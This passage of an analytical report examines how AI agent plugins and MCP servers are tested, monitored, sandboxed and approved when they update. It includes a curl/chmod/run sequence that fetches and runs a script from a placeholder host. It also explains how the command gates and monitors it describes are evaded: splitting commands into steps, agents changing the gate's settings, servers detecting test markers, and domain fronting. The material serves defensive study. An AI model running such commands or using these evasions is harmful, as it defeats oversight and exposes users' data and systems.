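If a tool's answers change for 5% of inputs, 32 requests have about an 81% chance of getting at least one changed answer. But one different answer may not exceed the threshold. In one test of 22 tools, altered versions that gave wrong answers to 5% of inputs passed for 14 of the tools, even when ProbeID sent every recorded request. Chen and colleagues later devised tighter thresholds that caught more of these changes.

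They also measured how much real tools change. They recorded answers from 59 read-only tools on 16 public MCP servers and repeated the requests eleven times over eleven weeks. Seven tools changed by more than their normal variation, although every server's recorded version stayed the same.

One of the seven tools recommends pages from the documentation for Amazon's cloud services. The distance between its answers and the recorded ones was 0.10 after a day, 0.54 after 22 days and 1.00 after 55 days, and it stayed there. Two other tools on the same server didn't change. Chen and colleagues attribute the drift to the online documentation service that the tool queries, but they didn't find a specific cause. Pinning the server's version had no effect on that service.

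Three weather tools returned different output because the weather had changed. The other three returned error messages in a different format after Chen and colleagues reinstalled the tools' servers at the same pinned versions. Those servers depend on a library whose version is not pinned.

An eighth tool appeared to change because someone had renamed a folder on the measuring machine and left a link in its place, which made a file server list two permitted folders instead of one. The server had not changed, and Chen and colleagues left this case out of their count. They say none of the changes in the other seven tools is evidence of malice. Someone still has to investigate the cause of any change that a replay detects.

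To see whether ProbeID could protect an agent, they replaced four servers with altered copies that had the same tool definitions but sometimes returned wrong values. An agent then attempted 16 tasks. Afterwards, Chen and colleagues repeated its calls on the original servers and counted an answer as corrupted if the original wouldn't have given it:

| | Without ProbeID | With ProbeID |
|---|---|---|
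| Corrupted calls | 93 of 1,476 (6.3%) | 20 of 1,159 (1.7%) |
| Tasks with a corrupted call | 15 of 16 | 9 of 16 |
| Calls refused | 0 | 102 |

ProbeID refused no calls when the agent used the original servers. The benchmark scored every task as successful in every run, including runs with corrupted values, so an agent's apparent success is poor evidence that its tools work properly.

The 20 remaining corrupted calls came from two tools whose changes weren't triggered by the recorded requests. One calculates a property of a matrix that the agent has stored under a name. The recorded requests used invented names, so the original and the altered copy both reported that no such matrix existed. Repeating those requests wouldn't expose the change. A better test would first store a matrix and then request the property.

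ProbeID made about 500 requests per check in this experiment. Checking only whether answers were identical, with at most 32 requests, left 22 corrupted calls and used about a fifteenth as many requests. This method is better for tools that always give the same answer, but it would raise false alarms for tools whose answers vary.

The requests also run the tool, so replaying calls to `record_invoice` in a real accounting system could add false invoices. That tool needs a test copy that can be reset. ProbeID checks only the answers, so it wouldn't detect the hidden copying in `postmark-mcp`, where the agent received the usual success message.

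### Checking each command

A skill's documentation poorly predicts the exact commands an agent will run. In a live run with 39 skills, *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* found that only 2 of the agent's 144 commands appeared verbatim in the documentation, and 34.7% had a type of consequence found in none of the documentation's code blocks. These commands all fell into the general class for shell commands, so in this small sample the agent didn't turn a mild instruction into a more severe type of action.

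Taneja and Weber therefore check the command itself. Their program, called a gate, inspects each command before it runs and uses fixed rules to sort it into one of 33 classes. Depending on the class and the record of earlier approvals, the gate lets the command run, holds it for a person to review or blocks it. Commands in 13 of the classes, including downloading and running code, can never run unattended, whatever their approval record. A check takes about 68 milliseconds.

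Taneja and Weber, who sell the gate, tested it on 53 skills that ClawHub had rated clean but whose documentation included an action in one of those thirteen classes. The agent tried such an action with 23 of the skills, and the gate stopped it every time. With 23 cases, the 95% confidence interval for the gate's success rate runs from 85% to 100%. They used one model and one prompt, and gave the agent at most four turns per skill.

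The setting wasn't adversarial, since nobody was writing commands to get past the gate. In a separate test with disguised commands, the gate recognized an average of 52% across eight techniques. It caught none of the cases that split a forbidden command into steps:

```
curl -o setup.sh https://tools.example/setup.sh
chmod +x setup.sh
./setup.sh
```

The first line downloads a file, the second makes it executable and the third runs it. The gate checks each command separately, so it doesn't detect that they are related. An agent may also split up the steps innocently. In the live run, after a command that downloads and runs a script failed, the agent downloaded the file separately and read it. An agent with shell access could also change the settings that start the gate, and the gate doesn't prevent this.

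An earlier run of the same kind found forbidden attempts with only 4 of 54 skills. The agent probably spent its turns checking whether its tools worked and never reached the installation step. The choice of skills also changed, so the two runs aren't strictly comparable. Still, a faulty test environment can make a plugin look safer than it is.

The gate made 170 interventions across the 53 skills, or 3.2 per skill. If an operator let ordinary shell commands run unattended, this would fall to 25. But it is hard to know when a class of command has earned that trust. Suppose a person has approved N actions in a row without finding a problem. The highest failure rate ε that this record can't rule out, at 95% confidence, satisfies

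(1 − ε)ᴺ = 0.05

The shipped gate uses ten approvals by default. Even if all ten are clean, the failure rate could be as high as 25.9%. Ruling out a rate above 5% takes 59 clean approvals. These figures assume that the actions are independent and that future actions resemble past ones. An update can break the second assumption, so it would be sensible to restart the count when an update widens a plugin's access.

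### New domains as a sign of drift

*MCPShield* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) combines checks before, during and after a tool's use. Before an agent uses a server, a language model invents arguments for the server's tools and compares the results with the tools' descriptions. During a call, the model decides which network domains the tool needs, and a sandbox blocks actions outside the permitted limits. After five calls, the system starts comparing recent behaviour with those first five, and it repeats the comparison every three calls.

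A language model scores the drift from 1 to 5, and by default a score of 4 can lead to rejection. A new domain is one of eleven signals it may report. Others include reading sensitive files, starting a program and asking for an API key. The model's instructions say that new domains can be benign, and that only behaviour that conflicts with the tool's description or has risky side effects should get a high score.

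This rule is reasonable because honest authors often add domains. But if the invoice plugin's description mentions PDF conversion, the judge is unlikely to give `convert.invoice-tools.example` a high drift score, even if the domain's operator keeps every invoice. A company that wants to know about every new recipient of its invoices should treat the domain as grounds for review, whatever its score.

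Zhou and colleagues tested MCPShield on 76 malicious servers with six language models. It stopped an average of 95.30% of attacks, compared with 10.05% without it. In a smaller test, servers turned malicious only after several calls. MCPShield stopped 79% to 98% of these attacks, depending on the model. With five of the six models, the checks during execution caught more than either of the other stages.

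On average, MCPShield wrongly flagged 2.35% of harmless servers with GPT-4o mini and 29.41% with Qwen3-235B, so the abstract's claim that it avoids false positives doesn't hold for every model. Its early test calls also carry a marker that identifies them as tests, and a malicious server could check for the marker and act harmless when it is present. One of the test servers ran its hidden file operations and network connections only during real calls.

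### Outbound allowlists

An outbound allowlist limits where a program can connect while it runs, so it can block an address that the program assembled from pieces and that a scan of its files missed. In Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code, for example, shell commands have no direct route to the network. They must go through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that compares the requested hostname with the allowlist.

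The sandbox is off until someone turns it on. Its list of allowed domains starts empty, and by default the user gets a prompt the first time a command needs a new domain. According to Anthropic, the user can allow the domain for that session or permanently. Administrators can instead block every unlisted domain without a prompt. In auto mode, Claude names the domains that a command needs, and a second model reviews them together with the command. Approval covers only that command, not the rest of the session.

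GitHub has a similar firewall for the cloud version of Copilot, its coding agent. It is on by default and allows access to common sources of software packages. When it blocks a request, it adds a warning to the pull request with the address and the command that tried to reach it, which is much more useful to a reviewer than a domain name alone. Since April 2026, administrators have been able to maintain one allowlist for the whole organization and stop individual repositories from adding to it, according to GitHub's *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent* (2026).

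Both products leave out much of what a plugin can run. GitHub's firewall doesn't cover MCP servers or the setup steps that run before the agent starts. Claude Code's sandbox doesn't cover MCP servers, hooks or the monitors that plugins can install. If the invoice plugin's local server contacts the converter, neither list blocks the connection. To cover these programs, Anthropic advises running all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or its separate sandbox software.

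A permitted domain can also serve many customers. Docker, which makes software for running programs in isolated environments, warns that allowing `github.com` allows everything on it, including content that users upload. An agent could publish a company's file there without contacting a new domain. GitHub's firewall can allow a full web address instead of a whole domain, which can limit access to one project's folder.

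By default, Claude Code's proxy doesn't decrypt traffic, so it can check the hostname but not what the program sends. The program supplies that hostname. With a technique called domain fronting, a program gives the proxy a permitted hostname but puts a different destination inside the encrypted request, and some hosting networks will send the request there. Anthropic lets companies use their own proxy with stricter rules instead. A proxy that decrypts traffic can check the real destination and look for sensitive data, but it also handles the company's secrets in readable form, so it needs strong protection.

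In its guide to secure deployment, Anthropic warns that an agent with broad credentials for a permitted service may be able to use that service to send data elsewhere. Narrowing a plugin's credentials can do more to prevent this than shortening its list of allowed domains.

### What tests and monitors still miss

A plugin can misbehave only under a rare condition, such as a certain date, a particular customer or its hundredth invoice. SkillSentry can create that condition in a test if the skill's files reveal it, but not if the plugin receives it later from a remote server. Monitoring continues after testing ends, so it is more likely to detect the behaviour. But by then the plugin is working with real data, and an alert can't undo an upload that has already happened.

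**Remote processing.** Zhou and colleagues tested servers that users run themselves and left better support for remote ones to future work. Monitoring on the user's machine can't track data once it reaches a remote server. A company could instead send the server a decoy invoice containing an email address that appears nowhere else. Mail to that address from a stranger would be strong evidence of a leak, but the server's operator might have copied the invoice even if no mail arrived.

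Taneja and Weber found skills on ClawHub whose risks their gate couldn't detect because the actions involved were permitted. One skill sent messages to a recipient fixed in its instructions, without asking the user. Another gave an agent far more access to private data than its purpose required, though no single action looked excessive. A scanner that reads the whole skill can compare its purpose with its access and may catch both. A gate could catch the first if it also checked recipients, but catching the second requires someone to decide how much access the skill needs.

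## Who approves a change: users, administrators and directory reviewers

Scanners and monitors can show that a plugin has gained access, but someone still has to decide whether it should have it. The user, an administrator at the user's company and a reviewer at the plugin directory each know something that the others don't:

| Approver | What they know | What they usually don't know |
|---|---|---|
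| User | The task, and whether a request fits it | What the code does, and what the company's contracts allow |
| Administrator | The company's rules, and which outsiders may hold its data | What each employee is doing when a request appears |
| Directory reviewer | The code, and the publisher's earlier releases | The user's task and the company's rules |

For version 2 of the invoice plugin, the accountant who uses it knows whether she wants automatic payment reminders. Her company's administrator knows whether the company has a contract with the PDF converter's provider. If the upload script ships with the plugin, a directory reviewer can check that it sends only the PDF. None of them can see what the converter does with the PDF after the upload.

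### Chrome's rule for updates that need more permissions

Google's browser, Chrome, asks the user about some updates to extensions. According to Google's *Permission warning guidelines*, if a new version adds a permission that carries a warning, Chrome disables the extension until the user accepts it. Chromium's *Extension Permissions*, which documents the open-source code behind Chrome, describes the comparison:

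1. Chrome keeps a list of every permission that the user has granted the extension and not revoked.
2. It compares the warnings for that list with the warnings for the permissions the new version requires.
3. If the new version needs a warning that the earlier grants don't cover, Chrome disables the extension and notifies the user.
4. The user can accept the new permissions and turn the extension back on.

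Because Chrome compares warnings and not the permissions themselves, it doesn't disable an extension for adding any of these:

- **A permission without a warning**, such as `storage`, which Chrome treats as relatively harmless.
- **A permission that a broader one covers.** An extension with access to every google.com page can add maps.google.com.
- **An optional permission.** Chrome asks about it when the extension first requests it, not when the update arrives.
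- **A permission that the user granted before.** If version 1 had a permission, version 2 dropped it and version 3 restores it, Chrome asks only those users who started with version 2.

The last exception is risky because an extension can be sold between versions 1 and 3, and a user who trusted the first owner hasn't agreed to anything with the second. Such sales have caused trouble for WordPress, the software behind many websites. Search Engine Journal's *WordPress Announces Initiative To Secure All Plugins And Themes* quotes WordPress on a case in which the owners of good plugins sold them without knowing the buyer was malicious.

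Chrome's rule would be hard to copy for AI plugins. Most have no enforced list of permissions, and many start with shell access, which covers nearly everything an update might add. The rule also gives users a poor choice between accepting the new permissions and giving up the extension. Chromium describes no way to keep running the old version.

### What users do with permission prompts

Early Android phones showed an app's permissions once, just before installation, and the user could accept them all or cancel. Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, surveyed 308 Android users online and watched another 25 install apps in a laboratory. In both groups, 17% paid attention to the permissions. In the laboratory group, 42% didn't know that permissions existed. Only 3% of the online group correctly answered all three questions about what particular permissions allowed. But a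 fifth of the laboratory group could describe cancelling an installation because of permissions, and Felt and colleagues suggested that such people could warn others through reviews.

Coding agents ask for approval much more often, sometimes before each command. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026) reported that users accept 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) later put the figure at 97%. People could accept this many prompts and still read them, because most of the commands are probably safe. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which suggests that they look at plans more closely, although they may also reject a plan because it is bad rather than dangerous.

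Anthropic also measured attention more directly in an experiment. A research vendor hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Auto mode, in which a language model checks each action in place of the user, blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). It missed only 6 of the commands that testers refused, so using both checks would have stopped 943.

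Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This looks like fatigue, although the people who got through 50 prompts may have been the ones who clicked fastest. The testers had nothing of their own to lose in the test environment, so they may have been less careful than they would be at work. Anthropic published the results to justify making auto mode the default. Even so, the gap between 13.6% and 89% is too large to dismiss.

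Auto mode also makes mistakes about consent. In Anthropic's earlier test, it let through 17% of 52 real actions by Claude that went beyond what the user had authorized. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" hasn't agreed to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

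Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, and 64% said they often approve at least one type of action without close review. The most common type, at 36%, was access to the internet, outside APIs and connected tools, which plugins often add. The overall rate was similar among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of an agent's code (61%) and those who didn't (67%), and the difference could be due to chance.

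Developers who knew about the risks weren't more careful. Of those who knew of a security or privacy incident or a worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who didn't. The difference remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which matters because heavy users might both hear of more incidents and approve more prompts. Developers who inspected diffs, which show the exact lines that changed, were less likely to skip close review when approving access to secrets or personal data, changes to production settings, or destructive commands. This is a reason to try showing diffs, though they may not be what made these developers careful.

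Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. Of the 107 who answered the questions about permissions, 47.7% said they read requests carefully and 33.6% said they had become less careful over time. Most used what they knew about the task, with 63.6% looking harder at unexpected requests and 67.3% less likely to grant a request that didn't fit what they had asked for. More than half (58.9%) said they would never give an agent access to email or other personal information, which would rule out even version 1 of the invoice plugin.

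The two surveys rely on volunteers' self-reports, and all of the recent evidence concerns an agent's actions during a task. People might read two plugin updates a month more closely than the hundredth command of the day, but none of these studies tested that. Closer reading would depend on asking few questions, and the re-approval rule that Ameur and colleagues tested on 39 tool servers still produced 645 questions about changed tools.

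### Consent for an added scope

When a plugin needs a new OAuth scope, the question can reach the user in the middle of a task. The Model Context Protocol calls the procedure step-up authorization. Suppose the accountant asks her agent to send a payment reminder, but the invoice plugin's token covers only reading mail. Under Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), the plugin's server should refuse the call with an error that names the missing scope:

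```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
  scope="mail.send",
  error_description="Sending reminders requires mail access"
```

When the application requests the wider token, the authorization server can ask the user to approve it, usually in a browser window. If she agrees, the application retries the call. Under the Model Context Protocol, applications should limit these retries, and servers should name all the scopes an operation needs at once so that the user doesn't have to approve several requests.

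This is a good moment to ask, because the accountant has just requested a reminder and can see why the plugin needs to send mail. But the protocol leaves the design of the consent screen to the authorization server and doesn't require the screen to separate the new scope from the old ones. Since the application requests them together, the screen might list them all without marking the new one. The explanation in the error message is optional, and the server's operator writes it.

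Some applications haven't supported the procedure well. In *MCP step‑up consent not exposed for insufficient scope* (2026), a user of Cursor 2.4.21 reported in February that the editor had no way to approve an added scope during a session, so users had to log out and repeat the whole consent process. If this happens often, developers have a reason to request every scope at the first login instead of adding them gradually.

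A scope also remains available after the task it was granted for. WorkOS, which sells login and authorization software, gives the example of an agent that deletes a production database using a scope the user granted three hours earlier. The request proceeds because the token is still valid. Step-up authorization asks the user only when a scope is missing, so it doesn't ask before a dangerous action that an existing scope allows. If the accountant agrees to `mail.send` for one reminder, the plugin can send other emails with the same token.

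### Why ten clean approvals are weak evidence

After a plugin has behaved well for a while, it is tempting to stop asking about it. But the ten clean approvals that Taneja and Weber's gate requires by default leave room for a failure rate of up to 25.9%. The same limit applies to updates if each one from a publisher has the same chance ε of being harmful, whatever happened with the others. The chance that N updates in a row are all harmless is then (1 − ε)ᴺ, which for ten updates falls to 5% at ε = 1 − 0.05^(1/10) ≈ 0.259. To rule out a rate of ε or more at 95% confidence, the number of clean approvals has to be at least

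N = ln 0.05 ÷ ln(1 − ε)

| Failure rate to rule out | Clean approvals needed |
|---|---|
| 10% | 29 |
| 5% | 59 |
| 1% | 299 |

A plugin with one update a month would need almost 25 years to collect 299 approvals.

The 25.9% is an upper limit, not an estimate of the next update's risk. In *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, Taneja and Weber note that if every failure rate were equally likely beforehand, the chance that the next run fails after ten clean ones would be 1 in 12, or about 8.3%. Other evidence may suggest a much lower risk for updates from an established company, but ten approvals add little to that evidence.

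Real updates also violate the calculation's assumption that trials are independent and similar, because a publisher chooses what goes into each version. Ten typo fixes provide almost no evidence about the safety of an update that adds `mail.send`. `postmark-mcp` had fifteen versions before the one that copied users' emails. Even if the assumption held, fifteen clean versions would be consistent with a failure rate as high as 18.1%, and an attacker who plans to make the sixteenth malicious can keep the first fifteen clean.

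The calculation also assumes that the reviewer notices every harmful update. If the reviewer catches only a share r of them, the chance of N approvals with no problem noticed becomes

(1 − rε)ᴺ

If r is 13.6%, the share of dangerous commands that Anthropic's testers caught, a reviewer would have a 23% chance of approving ten harmful updates in a row without noticing a problem. Ten clean approvals from such a reviewer therefore can't rule out any failure rate, even 100%.

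Taneja and Weber also point out that if a careful reviewer has been rejecting the bad actions, the clean record partly reflects the reviewer's work and can't show what will happen once the reviewer stops looking. Even if each update has only a 1% chance of being harmful, the chance of at least one harmful update in 100 is about 63%. It makes more sense to base an exemption on what an update changes, letting small updates through if they add no access and still asking about the rest.

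### Administrators and standing rules

An administrator can decide whether to approve a change once for a whole company. In Cursor, plugins must follow the company's lists of allowed and blocked MCP servers. If a plugin contains a blocked server, Cursor still installs the plugin, but the server can't make calls. If an update adds a server, that server therefore can't make calls until the company permits it.

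In Claude Code, administrators can set the default permission mode for everyone or turn auto mode off. They can also list actions that auto mode must always block, even if an employee asks for them. Anthropic already includes sending code or secrets to an outside destination among these actions. A company could add a rule against sending invoices to any service it hasn't approved. However, auto mode can apply the rule only to actions it sees, not to what a remote server does with the data.

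Good rules are hard to write in advance. Salerno and colleagues describe an experiment by Yan in which 113 people supervised a simulated day of an agent's actions. Rules participants wrote beforehand blocked less overreach than either approving each action or leaving the review to a model. Participants set most of their rules to "ask", then approved most of the overreach when asked. Professional administrators might do better, but there is little evidence on how well they judge plugin updates.

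An administrator's mistake also affects more people than a user's. With Anthropic's "Allow anyway" override, for example, one person's decision removes the warning for everyone with access to the plugin. Using the directory's findings as well could reduce this risk. Taneja and Weber suggest that if a registry rates a skill anything other than clean, a company could require approval for every action the skill takes, however good its record. They haven't tested this.

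### Directory reviewers at Cursor and WordPress

When a plugin's source code changes, Cursor's staff review the update by hand before publishing it to the marketplace, whereas some of Anthropic's publish settings let updates that pass the scan go live without a reviewer. Cursor requires marketplace plugins to be open source and says they contain no binaries (compiled programs that a reviewer can't easily read). It works with a small group of partners it trusts. If it finds that a plugin poses a risk, it removes the plugin immediately while someone fixes the problem.

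As documented, Cursor's review procedure is the most thorough of any large directory's. It probably depends on the marketplace staying small, but Cursor plans to accept plugins more broadly. Cursor gives no figures on how long updates wait, how often reviewers reverse a decision or how many threats they miss, so outsiders can't tell how long reviewers spend on each update.

The WordPress plugin directory lists ordinary software, not AI plugins, but it has the same problem with updates at a much larger scale. *Protect the Shire* (webhosting.today, 2026) reports that the review team had 4,740 items in its queue on June 1, 2026, and that 4,170 of them (88%) had waited more than seven days. The queued items appear to be mostly new plugins. Developers of existing plugins could make more than 3,000 commits in a single day, and none of them triggered an automated security review. Not every commit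 is a release, but a team with that backlog clearly couldn't read them all.

In June 2026, WordPress announced in *Protect The Shire* (2026) that it would wait 24 hours before automatically distributing plugin updates. It later cut the delay to 6 hours. During the delay, several AI models and a scanner called Jetpack Scan examine what changed from the previous version, and WordPress combines their findings into a risk score. Anthropic doesn't describe comparing versions this way for its own directory.

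*Automated security review for plugin releases* (Perez, 2026) describes an incident on July 28 that exposed a weakness in the first arrangement. Someone committed a backdoor to a plugin with about 20,000 active installations. The automated review gave the release a high score, but high scores didn't yet block releases. The plugin team closed the plugin 26 minutes after the security company Wordfence alerted them. WordPress never distributed the release, but only because people were available to act before the delay ended. In September, WordPress began blocking high-scoring releases automatically.

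*Automated Security Review*, WordPress's guide for plugin authors, says that a block covers only the flagged version. Websites keep the previous version, and the author can publish a corrected one, which goes through the same review. An author who thinks the finding is wrong can appeal, but WordPress says fixing the code is almost always faster. OpenAI gives developers much the same advice about appealing held tool changes.

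WordPress emails everyone who can commit to the plugin and shows them the file and line that caused the block. If an attacker has taken over one developer's account, the email may alert the others. But it also shows the attacker which line to rewrite before trying again, and WordPress has no equivalent of Anthropic's block on later versions.

WordPress stresses that its score measures risk, not intent, so an accidental security hole can score as high as malware. This is sensible, since both can harm a website. WordPress says its false positive rate is low but not zero, and doesn't give a figure. Neither Cursor nor WordPress appears to publish figures on reversed decisions or missed threats, so there is no good way to compare Cursor's reviewers with WordPress's models.

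### What an approval request should show

For version 2 of the invoice plugin, a useful request would contain at least this:

| Item | Example | How to check it |
|---|---|---|
| The exact difference | Adds `mail.send`, `convert.invoice-tools.example` and the free-text argument `notes` | Software compares the two versions |
| The author's reason | Payment reminders, PDF conversion and notes on partial payments | A reviewer compares it with the code |
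| The data affected | Every invoice PDF, and any mail that the agent copies into `notes` | A reviewer reads the code or runs a test |
| The destination's owner | The conversion company and its relationship to the author | The administrator looks for a contract |
| The option to refuse | Keep version 1, which has no known security holes | The directory checks published warnings |

An approval request should first show what changed in the plugin's permissions and network access, using a comparison generated by software, not the plugin's author. Anthropic removes Claude's explanations before auto mode judges an action, because they might persuade the checker to approve it. A person needs the author's reason for an addition to judge whether it makes sense, but the request should label that reason as the author's.

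*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) recommends tying each approval to the exact action and showing its combined consequence, since several permitted actions can add up to something forbidden. For the invoice plugin, the request should state that the plugin will be able to read private mail and send mail to anyone, which a user might not realize from "send payment reminders" alone.

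Approval of an update should apply to an exact set of files. Search Engine Journal's *When The Wordpress Plugin Update Is The Security Risk* describes an attack in October 2026 on Rank Math SEO PRO, a commercial plugin distributed outside WordPress's directory. Version 3.0.123 came out on October 7, but for about eleven hours on October 15 and 16, some customers who downloaded it got a copy with malware. A company that had approved "version 3.0.123" might have installed either copy. Checking the download against a fingerprint of the approved files would have exposed the difference.

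A request should also explain what the user can undo. Withdrawing `mail.send` stops future messages, but it doesn't bring back an invoice the converter has already received. It should be clear what a refusal covers, too. Salerno and colleagues recommend distinguishing between refusing one action and refusing a whole approach. If the accountant doesn't want her invoices to leave the company, the agent shouldn't look for another converter.

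Questions about a change can go to different people. The accountant can decide about the reminders, the administrator can decide about the converter, and the directory's reviewer can check whether the code matches the description. A system that sent all three questions to the accountant would be easier to build, but she would have to guess at two of the answers.

### Delayed security fixes

Holding an update for review can protect users from malicious code, but it leaves them exposed for longer when the update fixes a security hole that attackers already know about. GitHub's Dependabot, a tool that proposes updates to the packages a project uses, waits at least three days before proposing an ordinary new version but proposes a security fix as soon as someone publishes a warning about the flaw. Help Net Security's *GitHub delays version updates so malware gets caught first* (2026) cites a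 review of 21 well-known attacks, which found that each malicious version was caught within hours.

A three-day delay wouldn't have been enough for `postmark-mcp`, because Koi's report came eight days after the malicious release. It might not have helped with Rank Math either, because the tampering began eight days after version 3.0.123 came out, when a delay counted from the release date would already have ended. A GitHub product manager also told Help Net Security that a delay does little against a backdoor that stays dormant.

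WordPress's delay does more harm because it also applies to security fixes, according to Patchstack, a company that sells protection for WordPress sites. Patchstack tracked 114 releases in June and early July and found a median delay of 24.4 hours. Attackers exploited about half of high-impact flaws within 24 hours, according to Patchstack data reported in Search Engine Journal's *Report Shows WordPress Sites Are Getting Hacked At Faster Rate*. When Patchstack gave more weight to the most heavily attacked flaws, the median time to exploitation was 5 hours, which is shorter than WordPress's current delay of 6 hours.

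The delay can even help attackers, because a new release can be downloaded almost at once, while websites get the update notice later. An attacker can compare the corrected code with the old, find the flaw and use it before most sites have been offered the fix. Patchstack has a commercial interest in this criticism, since its product protects sites that haven't updated yet, but the problem is real. WordPress expects to shorten the delay to minutes eventually.

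An exception that lets security fixes skip the delay needs a safeguard, because attackers would label their own releases "security fix" if the label were enough. Dependabot avoids this by relying on a published warning about a known flaw. A plugin directory could do the same and also require that the fix add no permissions, tools or network destinations. Such an update should still go through an automatic scan, but it needn't wait for a person to review it.

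An update that both fixes a flaw and widens access is harder to decide on. If version 2 of the invoice plugin fixes a security flaw in version 1 and also adds the converter, the company must either keep the flaw or let the plugin send invoices to a new recipient. The directory could ask the author to release the fix separately. If that takes too long, the company can turn the plugin off until someone has reviewed the update, and the accountant can enter invoices by hand for a day.
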